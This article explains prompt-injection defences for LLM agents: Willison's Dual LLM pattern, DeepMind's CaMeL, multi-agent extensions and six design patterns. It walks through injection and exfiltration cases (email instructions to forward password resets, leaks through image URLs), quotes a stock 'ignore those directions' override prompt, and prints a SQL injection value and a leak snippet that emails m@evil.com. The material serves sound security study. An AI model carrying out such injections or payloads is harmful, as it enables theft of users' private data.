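# Simon Willison on CaMeL and the design patterns for securing LLM agents

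## What problem had Willison been trying to solve before 2025?

Prompt injection is an attack on software built around a large language model (LLM), the kind of program behind chatbots such as ChatGPT. The attacker puts instructions into text that the model reads as data, such as an email or a web page, and the model follows them. The attack is most dangerous for LLM agents, which are LLMs that can call tools to carry out a task for somebody, for example by sending email or reading files.

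On his *About me* page, Simon Willison describes himself as an independent open source developer who has blogged since 2002 and helped create the Django web framework. He coined the term "prompt injection" in September 2022.

In April and June 2025, Willison wrote up two papers on defending agents against prompt injection. One was Google DeepMind's account of a system named CaMeL, and the other was a catalogue of six design patterns. His enthusiasm for them makes more sense given the "alarmingly little progress" he complained of over the previous two and a half years in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025). He did not much like the best defence he himself had to offer in that time.

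### How text turns into actions

An LLM produces only text, so a developer who wants it to act has to turn some of that text into commands. Willison (2023) described the usual method in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*. The developer tells the model to write a line in a special format, such as `action:search_email(...)`, when a task requires searching the user's email. Ordinary code scans the output for that format, extracts the search terms, runs the search and pastes the results into the next prompt, and the model continues from there. Willison had written a working version in a few dozen lines of Python.

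The problem starts with pasting the emails into the prompt, which then contains the developer's instructions, the user's request and whatever strangers wrote in those emails. A filter could easily strip out an `action:` line planted in an email, but an attacker can instead write a plain English sentence asking for certain emails to be deleted. This works if it leads the model to write the `action:` line itself.

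All of this reaches the model as one sequence of tokens, the fragments of words that LLMs process. Willison called this joining of trusted and untrusted text the "original sin" of LLMs. In modern chat systems, developers try to keep the parts distinct by tagging each stretch of text as the user's words, the model's own reasoning or the output of a tool, and by training models to give these different degrees of authority.

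The tags affect models less than one would hope. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, trained simple classifiers on the internal activations of four models to detect which role each model was assigning to a piece of text. The training passages were identical except for their tags, so the classifiers could learn only the effect of the tag. The researchers then took 200 real conversations and put the users' messages inside tags that mark tool output. If the tags determined the role, the classifiers should have detected tool output almost every time. Instead, they gave user text a probability of 76 to 88 per cent and tool output at most 20 per cent. The models internally treat text that sounds like a user's request as a user's request, whatever its source.

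Those four models are mid-sized (20 to 120 billion parameters), and the largest commercial ones have become much harder to fool. In June 2026 Willison, in *163 posts tagged "prompt-injection"*, reported a public challenge in which about 6,000 attempts failed to extract a secret from an email assistant, though he added that this was no guarantee against a cleverer attacker.

### The comparison with SQL injection

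In September 2022 Riley Goodside posted a prompt directing GPT-3, OpenAI's model at the time, to translate a sentence from English to French. The sentence contained an instruction to ignore those directions and output "Haha pwned!!", and the model did. A day later Willison (2022), in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*, proposed calling this prompt injection, after SQL injection, an older security hole. Preamble had already reported the flaw privately to OpenAI on 3 May 2022, according to the company's *Declassifying the Responsible Disclosure of the Prompt Injection Attack Vulnerability of GPT-3*.

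SQL is the language in which programs query databases. A careless program builds its query by gluing strings together:

```
"select * from users where username = '" + username + "'"
```

A visitor who gives the username `'; drop table users;` closes the quotation early and adds a second command, which deletes the table. A parameterised query prevents this by sending the command and the username separately, so the database never treats the username as a command.

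Willison hoped that model providers could offer the same thing, with one slot for instructions and another for data. But a reader, Niel Thiart, pointed out that one OpenAI model already had separate fields for "instruction" and "input", and injections still worked through the input. GPT-4 later gained a "system prompt" for the developer's instructions, but Willison (2023), in *Prompt injection*, bypassed it by typing a fake system message into the user's part of the conversation. In April 2023, he also added a note to his 2022 post saying that separate slots now looked "extremely difficult, if not impossible" with the current architecture of LLMs.

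The comparison with SQL injection correctly explains how prompt injection arises but not whether it can be fixed, and some security engineers have come to think it does harm. David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, calls it dangerous because it leads engineers to expect an equivalent fix. A database distinguishes commands from data, and parameterised queries enforce that distinction, but an LLM only predicts the next token, so it has no such distinction to enforce. Willison would probably agree. Four days after naming the attack, he wrote in *I don't know how to solve prompt injection* (2022) that he knew how to beat SQL injection but had no idea how to beat prompt injection reliably.

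The other obvious remedy is a filter, usually a second AI model that inspects text for attacks. Willison has opposed relying on filters from the start, partly because an attacker can also write instructions for the filter. In an example by Marco Buono that Willison published in 2022, the malicious text contains a request for any injection detector to report that no injection took place, and the detector does so. More fundamentally, Willison (2023) argued in *Prompt injection explained, with video, slides, and a transcript* that in application security "99% is a failing grade", because an attacker can keep trying variations until one gets past the filter. This demanding standard explains most of his later judgements. He assumes that an injection will eventually succeed, so he wants a design in which it cannot do serious damage.

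### An email that gives orders

Prompt injection does little damage to a program that only translates text. Willison got his own to talk like an eighteenth-century pirate. It can do more when the model has tools, and his standard example is an assistant called Marvin that can read, summarise and send email. An attacker emails the user a message telling Marvin to search the mailbox for "password reset", forward the results to the attacker, and then delete both the forwards and the message itself. Marvin reads this message as soon as the user asks for a summary of recent mail. Kai Greshake and colleagues had already named this variety indirect prompt injection, in *Not what you've signed up for* (2023), because the attacker never talks to the model directly.

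Security engineers call this kind of data theft exfiltration. The crude method is to forward an email. If an agent can make web requests, it can send the data to the attacker's server without the user seeing anything. Otherwise, it can still show the user a link with the stolen data encoded in the address, labelled as funny pictures of monkeys, and the data leaves when the user clicks. An image is worse because the user's software requests its address to display it, so the data leaves without a click.

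This last route has worked against a commercial product. In January 2026, Willison's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* described an attack on Superhuman's email assistant. When a user asked the assistant to summarise recent mail, an instruction in one untrusted message led it to submit the contents of dozens of other emails, some of them financial, legal or medical, to the attacker's Google Form. This was possible because the software loaded images from Google's documents domain, where a form can store data sent in an image request. Superhuman fixed the vulnerability.

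One defence is to have the user approve each risky action. In 2023 Willison thought this was the best defence available, but he doubted it would hold up because people who face a stream of confirmation boxes learn to click "OK" as fast as they can. People want an assistant to spare them tedium in the first place.

### Two models and a controller

Willison's proposal of 25 April 2023 assumes that nobody can stop a model from obeying hidden instructions, so a model that reads untrusted content must not be able to do anything harmful. Under his rules, such a model may take no action that an attacker could abuse. If private data is mixed in with what it reads, it also may not produce outbound links or images, and it may contact only services that will not leak the data. Willison admitted that these rules seem to exclude most of what people want an assistant for.

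The Dual LLM pattern gets some of that back by dividing the assistant into parts.

- The **privileged LLM** takes the user's request, plans the work and can use tools. It never sees untrusted content.
- The **quarantined LLM** reads untrusted content and has no tools. The design assumes that it may "go rogue at any moment".
- The **controller** is ordinary software with no language model in it. It talks to the user, starts the two models, runs the tools and keeps the data.

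*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) describes the arrangement as a separation of duty, in which one model makes the decisions and only the other reads the suspect material. The controller passes names between them instead of text. Willison's example begins with a user asking for a summary of their latest email.

1. The controller hands the request to the privileged LLM, which replies with an instruction to fetch one email and store it as `$VAR1`.
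2. The controller fetches the email and stores its text under that name. The privileged LLM learns that `$VAR1` exists and nothing about what is in it.
3. The privileged LLM asks for the quarantined LLM to summarise `$VAR1`.
4. The controller replaces the name with the actual text of the email and sends the result to the quarantined LLM, which writes a summary.
5. The controller stores the summary as `$VAR2` and tells the privileged LLM only that the job is complete.
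6. The privileged LLM composes a reply for the user, an introductory phrase followed by `$VAR2`.
7. The controller puts the summary in place of the name and displays the reply.

By the end, each part has seen the following.

| | Controller | Privileged LLM | Quarantined LLM |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user's request | Yes | Yes | No, only the order to summarise |
| Text of the email | Yes | No, only the name `$VAR1` | Yes |
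| Text of the summary | Yes | No, only the name `$VAR2` | Yes, having written it |
| Tools | Runs them | Can request them | None |

Suppose the email is the one addressed to Marvin. The quarantined LLM may well follow the email's instructions, but it can only write text, which goes into `$VAR2` and then to the screen. The user would then get a strange or dishonest summary, but no password resets would be forwarded, because the only model that can order a forward never receives those instructions.

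This holds only as long as the two models are kept separate. In 2023, developers were increasingly chaining prompts, feeding the output of one into the next. Willison warned that an injection can spread through such a chain, because a manipulated model can repeat the malicious instruction in its output. Anything derived from the quarantined LLM's output therefore has to stay on the quarantined side, no matter how many steps it has passed through.

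He allowed one exception. If the quarantined LLM has to sort a text into one of a fixed set of categories, the controller can check that the output is exactly one of those categories and pass it to the privileged LLM. The developer wrote the categories, so the output can't contain a new instruction. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser et al., 2025) restates the pattern with both options, the checked output and the symbolic name, and renames the controller the "orchestrator".

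The exception matters more than its one paragraph in Willison's post suggests, because without it the privileged LLM gets no information from untrusted text. That is fine for summarising email, but *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of an agent that fixes bugs in a large body of code and may not read the bug reports, since a stranger could have written them. The agent would have to guess what was wrong. The paper widens the exception from fixed choices to include whole numbers, decimals and true-or-false values, so that the quarantined model can return, for instance, the line number of the bug. None of these values can carry a command, but any of them can be false, so an attacker who controls the report can still send the agent to the wrong line.

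### "Pretty bad"

Near the end of the post, Willison himself called the solution "pretty bad". He expected it to make assistants less pleasant to use and much more complicated to build, and the complexity worried him most. Every new feature gives developers another chance to accidentally let untrusted text reach the privileged LLM, and one such mistake undoes the whole protection.

The pattern also doesn't protect users from social engineering. It treats whatever the user types as trusted, so an attacker can reach the privileged LLM by persuading someone to paste in malicious text. An attacker's email could also make the quarantined LLM encode everything in its prompt as gibberish and tell the user to paste it into a certain website to receive a picture of a monkey. This exposes little if the prompt contains only the attacker's email, but if the user asks for a summary of the last ten emails,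 the prompt may also contain nine private ones. Willison distrusts AI filters, but he made a partial exception here and suggested using a model to warn users of such tricks, since a false alarm would do little harm.

A week later, in a talk, he called the pattern "a terrible solution" that might still be the best available for the moment. In 2025, DeepMind's researchers pointed out another weakness, which he had missed. The quarantined LLM can return a false value, such as the wrong email address, which the privileged LLM then uses without seeing it. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, confirms with machine-checked proofs that such a corrupted answer can leak data when the values are untagged, even though the injection cannot add its own tool call.

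## How does CaMeL work, and why did Willison find it credible?

DeepMind's researchers showed the flaw in the Dual LLM pattern with an example. A user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and adds that Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The privileged LLM plans the work without reading the notes. Its plan is to find the notes, extract the address and document name, fetch the document, and send it. Extracting the details requires reading untrusted content, so the quarantined LLM does that step.

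Suppose an attacker adds a line to those notes telling any AI that reads them to give the attacker's address as Bob's. The quarantined LLM does so, and the document goes to the attacker, even though the attacker hasn't added, removed or reordered any steps. The document's name comes from the same notes, so the attacker could also choose a more valuable file.

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes two properties. An agent has control flow integrity if the planner alone determines which actions run, in what order and under what conditions. It has data flow security if untrusted data cannot corrupt the inputs to those actions or the values that determine which branch of the plan runs. The Dual LLM pattern guarantees only control flow integrity.

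Garby and colleagues give a sense of how many attacks this leaves possible. They used the banking part of AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents carry out simulated tasks while attackers plant instructions in the material the agents read. In 97 of its 144 pairings of a task with an attack, the attack needs an action that the user's task doesn't require, such as a transfer when the user only wanted a summary of recent transactions. Separating the two models generally stops these attacks. In the other 47, the legitimate plan may already contain every action the attacker needs.

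### A plan written as code

CaMeL, short for "CApabilities for MachinE Learning", keeps the two models but has the privileged LLM write its whole plan as a program before anything reads untrusted content. DeepMind chose a restricted version of Python because LLMs already write Python well. If the user wants the assistant to find Bob's address in the latest email and remind him about tomorrow's meeting, the program in Willison's example looks roughly like this:

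```
email = get_last_email()
address = query_quarantined_llm("Find Bob's address in [email]",
                                output_schema=EmailStr)
send_email(recipient=address, subject="Meeting tomorrow", body="...")
```

The `output_schema` setting requires the quarantined LLM to format its answer as an email address. This rules out a paragraph of instructions, but not the attacker's email address.

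Standard Python would run these lines without recording where `address` came from. DeepMind therefore wrote its own interpreter, the software that executes the program. It attaches tags, called capabilities in CaMeL, to each value to record where the data came from and who may read it. Any value computed from another inherits its history.

| Value | Origin | Status |
|---|---|---|
| `email` | The user's inbox | Untrusted |
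| `address` | The quarantined LLM's reading of `email` | Untrusted, because it derives from `email` |
| `subject` and `body` | The privileged LLM, working from the user's request | Trusted |

Before each tool call, the interpreter applies a security policy. In Willison's example, the agent may always fetch the last email, but it may send email only to a trusted recipient. If the quarantined LLM returns an address that the user's policies list as trusted, the system sends the reminder without asking the user. If the address is unknown, the system can ask the user to approve the message. The attacker's address would be unknown, so the theft would require the user's approval.

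An attacker could still substitute another of the user's trusted contacts, and this rule would let the message through. That hardly matters for a reminder, but it would for a confidential document, which a policy can protect by using the tags on who may read the data. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a policy that forbids sending anything derived from private data to a person who may not read that data. Under this policy, the document in the first example could go only to its permitted readers, whatever address the quarantined LLM returned.

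When Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on the banking tasks, some injections succeeded with the policy checks off. None succeeded with the checks on, but the checks also halved the share of legitimate tasks that CaMeL completed. Separating the models should have been enough to stop two of the successful attacks. In those cases, the user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged LLM fixed the plan in advance, as CaMeL requires, but it wrote a program with a branch for every available tool, so the program would carry out whatever instructions the file contained.

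### Tags, not keys

"Capability" is a confusing name for these tags. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) defines a capability in classic computer security as an unforgeable token that both identifies an object and carries rights to it. For example, only a program that holds the token for a file can open that file. A CaMeL tag describes a piece of data for a separate policy to check, and grants no rights itself.

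After Karp (2025), in *Capabilities and prompt injection*, shared news of CaMeL with a mailing list on the subject, Mark S. Miller replied that CaMeL's tags "don't even sound vaguely like ocaps". Miller had coined "ocaps", short for object-capabilities, because people used "capabilities" too loosely for it to mean anything. He recognised the tags as taint tracking, an older technique for following suspect data through a program. He thought it could be very valuable here, but that it could not provide the hard guarantees claimed for CaMeL. Taint tracking is a good safeguard against innocent programming mistakes, but a fallible programmer could, with some tiny probability, write anything that a malicious one would.

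Miller called this a brief and cursory reaction, and he was responding to a summary of CaMeL. Garby and colleagues later found a gap of the kind he had in mind. CaMeL correctly blocks a program that emails an outsider only if the user's bank balance exceeds some threshold. The message itself contains nothing private, but its arrival would reveal something about the balance. The same leak succeeds with a detour, which follows a pattern known since the 1970s:

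```
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and receives a private tag. The fourth line then does nothing. The interpreter tags only the assignments it runs, so `rich` stays true and untagged. The last line depends on a variable that looks public, so the email goes out.

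A second gap is outside the interpreter, in an ordinary loop that retries failed programs. Whether a policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so each retry can reveal one more bit of it. CaMeL also has no proof that its tracking is sound.

An attacker would find it hard to exploit either gap. The privileged LLM writes the program without ever reading the attacker's text, so the leaking pattern would have to arise by accident or from the user's own request. The gaps therefore weaken CaMeL's claim to "guarantee" security more than they weaken its everyday protection.

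### What persuaded Willison

Willison called CaMeL "the first credible prompt injection mitigation" he had seen that did not "just throw more AI at the problem". CaMeL does run two LLMs, but an article quoted by Schneier (2025), in *Applying Security Engineering to Prompt Injection Security*, attributes its novelty to the architecture rather than the number of models. Willison objects to relying on a model to judge whether a text is an attack. In CaMeL, ordinary code decides whether the email goes out by checking tags against rules, and the email's wording cannot affect that check.

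Willison still objects to detectors for the reason he gave in 2023, that catching 99 per cent of attacks is a failing grade. If each attempt had an independent 1 per cent chance of getting through, an attacker would have a 63 per cent chance of succeeding at least once in a hundred attempts, and a more than 99 per cent chance in five hundred. He compares this with SQL injection, where nobody would accept a fix that failed once in a hundred tries.

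Real attempts are not independent, so the arithmetic somewhat overstates the problem. Narisetty and colleagues cite Anthropic's figures for its model Claude Opus 4.5 as a coding agent. Attackers succeeded 4.7 per cent of the time with one attempt, 33.6 per cent with ten and 63 per cent with a hundred. If the attempts had been independent, the last figure would have been 99 per cent. Even so, a defence that looks good against one attempt can fail more often than not against an attacker who makes a hundred.

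*The Attacker Moves Second*, an October 2025 study by 14 researchers, tested 12 published defences with attacks that adapted to each one. The attacks got past most of them more than 90 per cent of the time, as Willison (2025) summarised in *New prompt injection papers*. A later experiment suggests that Willison was right to distinguish defences that rely on the model from those that don't. In *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026), an automated attacker refined its methods over hundreds of rounds against nine configurations. Every defence that relied on the model to protect itself eventually leaked secrets. The only defence that held used ordinary application code to check the model's output, and it withstood 15,000 attacks.

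None of this tests CaMeL directly. Narisetty and colleagues warn that researchers have mostly tested CaMeL and similar systems on fixed sets of attacks, as they did with the defences that looked good and later failed. They ran an adaptive test on Progent, a related system that checks each tool call against rules. Progent cut attack success from 25.8 to 4.2 per cent, and an attack they designed to get around it did no better, succeeding 2.6 per cent of the time. The test covered only one small model and one style of attack, so it is weak evidence, but it supports Willison's view.

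Detection has meanwhile improved a great deal. In August 2026, Willison (2026) discussed an evaluation Anthropic had commissioned that included tests of its newest models in Claude Code, its coding agent. With an automatic safety check switched on, none of 720 injection attempts against those models succeeded. Willison said he would love to believe the problem was solved, but asked for more independent confirmation.

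Willison also had confidence in CaMeL because it relies on data flow analysis and access control, which are old, well-tested ideas in security engineering. It was also the first mitigation he had seen whose designers claimed strong guarantees, and he thought security researchers would not make such a claim lightly. The gaps in the tag tracking weaken this second reason more than the first.

Willison also pointed out a privacy benefit. The privileged LLM has to be a capable model because it plans and writes code, but the quarantined LLM handles simpler tasks, such as extracting an address from an email, so it could be a small model running on the user's own machine. The company hosting the privileged LLM would then see the user's request but not the emails or files that the tools return.

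Willison admitted that he was so positive about CaMeL partly because it builds on his own Dual LLM pattern. In a Hacker News discussion, he said he was "particularly tickled" that a DeepMind paper had a section headed "Is Dual LLM of Willison enough?" (he summarized the answer as "it is not"). Schneier, a well-known security expert with no such stake, also thought CaMeL seemed an important advance. But he gave it only one sentence and referred readers to Willison for the analysis, so his endorsement adds only a little independent support. By June 2025, Willison described CaMeL more narrowly, as a credible solution to "some of the challenges" of prompt injection in agents.

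### Attacks that CaMeL does not stop

CaMeL controls actions, so it doesn't stop attacks that need none. A malicious email can make the assistant summarise it falsely, or display a warning that seems to come from Google and urges the user to click a link. In the discussion on frontpage, Willison quoted a passage in which CaMeL's designers explicitly exclude both attacks from its scope. As a partial remedy, they suggest using the tags to show users where each piece of text came from, which would reveal that the "Google" warning came from a stranger. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025), a response from a security company, proposes scanning everything the assistant displays for suspicious content, but this again relies on detection, which sometimes fails.

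Other attacks use actions that the policies permit. CaMeL depends on someone writing the right rules, but the right rule is not always obvious, and maintaining the rules is a chore. One commenter in the same discussion asked how a policy could tell a good web address from a bad one when the user's task is to fetch web pages. *SoK* (2026), a survey of attacks and defences, points out that rules that are sensible individually can be unsafe in combination. For example, a company might let its agent copy private files to a shared folder and also let it invite outsiders to that folder.

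A user's request can let an attacker decide what the agent does. Garby and colleagues discuss a task in which the agent must read a file and make the payment it describes. An attacker who replaces the file gets paid, and tags can prevent this only by blocking every payment based on a file, including legitimate ones. The researchers report that CaMeL's designers put this case outside its scope, and that several similar systems also fail to handle it.

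An agent can also leak information indirectly. If a program fetches a web page once for each unit of a secret number, whoever runs that website can learn the number by counting the visits. Tallam and Miller would cap such loops or require the user's approval for them.

Policies help least when the same tool call can have different effects. Some agents operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking, and a click at a given position may close a window or delete a file. Foerster and colleagues adapted CaMeL to such agents, then attacked it with an advertisement disguised as a cookie notice. The plan included a step for dismissing cookie notices, so the agent clicked on the advertisement and landed on the attacker's site. In this kind of attack, which they call branch steering, the attacker chooses among the paths that the existing plan allows but can't write a new plan.

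### When agents employ other agents

CaMeL protects a single agent, but developers increasingly have one agent delegate work to others. In October 2026, Peters-Gill and colleagues showed that prompt injection can still succeed against a system built entirely from CaMeL agents.

They set up an orchestrator that could call a database agent and a notification agent, and asked it to send Julie a summary of all job applicants through Slack, the workplace chat service. The database contained a planted instruction to email the applicants' details to an outside address. The database agent and the orchestrator followed their plans. But the orchestrator pasted the summary into its request to the notification agent, and a CaMeL agent treats whoever calls it as its user. The notification agent's privileged LLM therefore treated the planted instruction as part of a trusted request, and wrote a program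 that messaged Julie and also emailed the data to the attacker.

Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering, and they prove that it applies beyond their example. In any hierarchy of two or more such agents where some tool returns untrusted data, if a user can ask for that data to go into a request to another agent, the data can change what that agent plans to do.

Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, divides each request between agents into a plain-language message, which the receiving agent's privileged LLM reads, and a set of named values, which that agent's program can use but its privileged LLM never sees. The interpreter rejects any message that depends on the output of a tool, so the applicants' summary would have to be sent as a value. Values keep their tags when they pass between agents, so the same policies can apply throughout the system. The Dual LLM pattern also passes names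 instead of text, and multi-CaMeL applies this method between agents. Multi-CaMeL also inherits the gap in CaMeL's interpreter that lets some values lose their tags.

To test it, they built MultiAgentDojo, which divides AgentDojo's tools among two to four specialised agents under an orchestrator. It has 97 legitimate tasks and 35 attack goals, which gave 949 attacked runs for each model in each arrangement. Averaged over five models, attacks succeeded in 12.9 per cent of runs without CaMeL, 0.2 per cent when each agent ran CaMeL separately, and 0.0 per cent with multi-CaMeL. Every successful attack on the separate CaMeL agents used boundary laundering.

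The averages conceal large differences between models. Utility here is the share of legitimate tasks completed with no attack under way.

| Model | Attack success, no CaMeL | Utility, no CaMeL | Utility, separate CaMeL agents | Utility, multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 69.1% | 53.6% | 52.6% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 86.6% | 73.2% | 66.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 78.4% | 38.1% | 24.7% |
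| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 76.3% | 42.3% | 26.8% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 27.8% | 13.4% | 7.2% |

Fable 5's scores are low because it refused 52 of the 97 harmless tasks. It may have associated the benchmark with attacks. On the remaining 45 tasks, its utility fell only from 91.1 to 84.4 per cent under either form of CaMeL. Stronger models generally lose less utility under CaMeL, and the same pattern appeared on AssetOpsBench, a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks. Running CaMeL on each agent lowered AssetOpsBench scores by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by 13.4 for Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Multi-CaMeL increased the loss for those two models by less than one point.

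All of these runs had the security policies switched off, so they measure only whether an attacker could change an agent's plan. Switching the policies on would also protect the data, but would probably reduce utility further. The models that gained the most security, GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro, lost about two-thirds of their utility under multi-CaMeL. The two strongest models kept most of their utility, but the benchmark's attacks rarely worked on them even without CaMeL. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn against concluding that such models are safe without CaMeL, because adaptive attacks have beaten every leading model tested at large scale.

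## What do the six design patterns allow an agent to do, and what do they forbid?

CaMeL needs a custom interpreter and a set of policies, but many agents can use something simpler. The design patterns paper, which Willison reviewed on 13 June 2025, describes CaMeL's approach alongside five others and applies them to ten example applications. Willison says it has eleven authors, but the citation in his post lists fourteen, from organisations including IBM, Google, Microsoft and ETH Zurich. Three of the authors, Edoardo Debenedetti, Daniel Fabian and Florian Tramèr, also worked on CaMeL.

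Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think general-purpose agents are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees while they depend on the current class of language models. They propose instead that people build agents for particular jobs and deliberately limit what those agents can do, so that they can do useful work today and still resist prompt injection.

### The guiding principle

All six patterns require that once an agent has read untrusted content, that content cannot trigger a consequential action, meaning one that harms the system or its surroundings. At a minimum, the agent must not be able to call tools that could corrupt or disclose data. Its output must also be harmless, without links that leak data or text that could manipulate the agent later.

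Dongol describes a real case of the last of these, an attack on ChatGPT's long-term memory reported in 2024. A web page got ChatGPT to store an instruction, which ChatGPT loaded into every later conversation. Its answers then displayed an image whose URL carried the user's messages to the attacker.

Willison's version of the rule is blunter. He assumes that an attacker who can get any text into a prompt controls everything the model does next, including its tool calls.

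Dongol has proved that, under a strict form of the rule, an injection cannot leak anything that the agent's plan would not have revealed anyway. As soon as the agent first reads untrusted content, software outside the model permanently withdraws every tool that an injection could call. The withdrawal has to be immediate because if the agent reads an attacker's email and then a secret while it still has those tools, the injection can use them to send the secret out. The proof covers agents with a fixed plan and assumes that each injection makes a single tool call.

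An agent secured this way is less useful because it can no longer answer an email after reading it. The six patterns differ mainly in how much of this lost usefulness they are designed to restore.

### The six patterns

Of the six patterns, the action-selector pattern allows an agent to do the least. The LLM translates a request into one of a fixed list of actions. For example, a customer service chatbot could give customers a link to their last order or send them to the page for changing a password. The LLM never sees what an action returns, so malicious text in a tool's results cannot affect it. But the agent also can't respond to those results, and it may refuse a reasonable request that its developers did not foresee.

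Plan-then-execute lets an agent use the results of its tools, but only after it has committed to a list of tool calls. If a user asks it to send today's schedule to their boss, John Doe, it plans to read the calendar and then email John. A malicious calendar entry cannot add a step or change the recipient, but it can rewrite the message. This falls short of the guiding principle, because an email sent in the user's name with an attacker's words can do harm. Even a harmless-looking plan to find and move files can be dangerous, since an injection could make the assistant find sensitive files and copy them to a public network drive.

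Suppose an agent using the map-reduce pattern has to find this month's invoices and email them to the accounting department. A separate LLM reads each file and answers only yes or no to whether it is an invoice. The agent collects the files that got a yes, and another LLM writes and sends the email. An attacker can get a malicious file counted as an invoice, but a fake invoice would achieve the same thing. The protection depends on the last LLM using the yes-or-no answers without reading the files.

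This pattern suits work that divides into independent pieces, such as screening CVs or comparing product reviews. Jacob and colleagues tested a similar idea on a shopping agent. A quarantined model gave each review two scores from 0 to 10, one for how strongly it supported the product and one for its relevance. A dishonest review could still receive misleading scores, but the agent saw only the median scores and the number of reviews. In 31.7 per cent of cases without this protection, an injected review turned the agent away from a product it would otherwise have chosen. With the protection, no attack succeeded, and the share of successful purchases barely changed, from 21.8 to 22.4 per cent.

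Beurer-Kellner and colleagues treat map-reduce as a special case of Willison's Dual LLM pattern, in which the privileged LLM refers to untrusted text by name but never reads it. They extend the Dual LLM pattern to code-then-execute, in which the LLM writes its plan as a program, as in CaMeL. A program can include loops and conditions, so it can handle more tasks than a list of steps. But in the example of John Doe's schedule, a malicious calendar entry can still change the message. CaMeL uses tags to track data, and its policies can block some uses of corrupted data. Willison emphasises this tracking in his summary of the pattern, but Beurer-Kellner and colleagues' definition does not require tags, so a developer could follow it and get only the protection of a fixed plan.

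Context-minimization addresses a different threat, in which the attacker may be the user. Suppose a customer asks a chatbot for a quote on a new car and adds instructions meant to get a large discount. The system turns the request into a database query, then deletes the customer's message before the LLM writes its reply, so the instructions are no longer in the LLM's context.

Willison was "slightly confused by this one". He took it to mean that the injection fails if the data returned from the database cannot include any text from the original request. A case study of a medical chatbot supports his reading. The chatbot summarises a patient's symptoms, consults a database or a doctor, and then explains the diagnosis. If the system deletes the patient's message but keeps the summary, an injection can survive in the summary. Deleting the summary as well prevents this, but then the chatbot cannot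 respond to what the patient said when it explains the diagnosis. A third option is to record the symptoms on a structured form with no free text.

| Pattern | What an attacker can still do | What the agent loses |
|---|---|---|
| Action-selector | Trigger a listed action through the user's request | Any response to what its tools return |
| Plan-then-execute | Change the contents of a planned action | The ability to change course after seeing a result |
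| Map-reduce | Change the result for the attacker's own document | Tasks that do not divide into separate pieces |
| Dual LLM | Falsify values that the plan uses | Decisions based on the meaning of untrusted text |
| Code-then-execute | Falsify values, unless tags and policies block their use | Steps that the program did not provide for |
| Context-minimization | Distort the query drawn from the request | Replies that take account of the user's own words |

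Beurer-Kellner and colleagues recommend combining patterns, since no single pattern is likely to be enough for every application. They also recommend ordinary precautions for every agent, such as running its actions in a sandbox (an isolated environment) and giving it no more access than its user has.

### An assistant for email and calendars

One of the ten applications is an assistant that reads and acts on a user's email and calendar. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues expect it to lose little usefulness with a fixed plan, because the steps it should take rarely depend on untrusted content. For example, a user might ask it to tell their regular collaborators about a holiday. The request alone determines the steps, although the plan needs a loop because the number of collaborators isn't known in advance.

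In a harder example from the paper, the user asks the assistant to reply to an email with whatever information the sender wants, using the user's recent mail. The steps are still predictable, but the sender influences what the assistant looks for. A hidden instruction could make it search for additional sensitive information and encode this in the reply using invisible characters, so the user could approve the draft without noticing.

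The Dual LLM pattern does not solve this. The quarantined LLM that drafts the reply has to see both the attacker's email and the private information, so it can include that information in its reply to the attacker. Dongol's proof that untagged values can leak data concerns a very similar agent, which uses a user's private notes to answer an outsider's email. CaMeL-style tags stop the leak, but they also block the legitimate reply because it is based on the same notes. The estimate that little usefulness is lost is therefore fair for the holiday message but too optimistic for this request.

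Some of the danger comes from what the user has authorised. In another of Dongol's examples, a user lets an agent send her calendar to anyone who requests a meeting. An attacker gains nothing by injecting an instruction to send the calendar, since a meeting request would have worked too. If the injection also gets the agent to send a password reset code, it reveals something a meeting request would not have, and Dongol counts only this second case as a security failure.

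Having the user confirm each email would catch cruder attacks. Reviewing drafts is fairly easy on a desktop computer but harder through a voice interface. Exempting messages to colleagues would be risky because, as Beurer-Kellner et al. point out, an attacker could use such a message to ask a colleague to approve a security-sensitive action.

Arranging a meeting by email is an exception to their assumption about untrusted content, because the assistant has to read the other person's reply to decide whether to accept a time or propose another. Jacob and colleagues had a quarantined model reduce each reply to a list of one-hour slots, which the privileged model compared with the user's calendar. They tested this on 100 simulated pairs of people, using OpenAI's GPT-4o. Attacks extracted private calendar details in 63 per cent of email threads without the defence and in none with it. The assistant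 successfully scheduled 90 per cent of meetings without the defence and 91 per cent with it. The defence didn't reduce scheduling success because times fit into a fixed list, unlike most of what people write in emails.

### A database agent that cannot see its results

The SQL agent loses much more functionality. It writes database queries to answer questions such as which of two products has the better sales outlook, and it writes Python code to analyse the results and draw charts. An undefended version checks the output and revises its queries and code until it has a satisfactory answer.

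If attackers may have written some of the data, the LLM cannot safely read it. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues therefore have the LLM write the query and the analysis code in advance, and only the code processes the data. The agent can still run a query and produce a chart. But it can't tell whether the data answers the question, so it can't, for instance, notice that a column is empty and try another.

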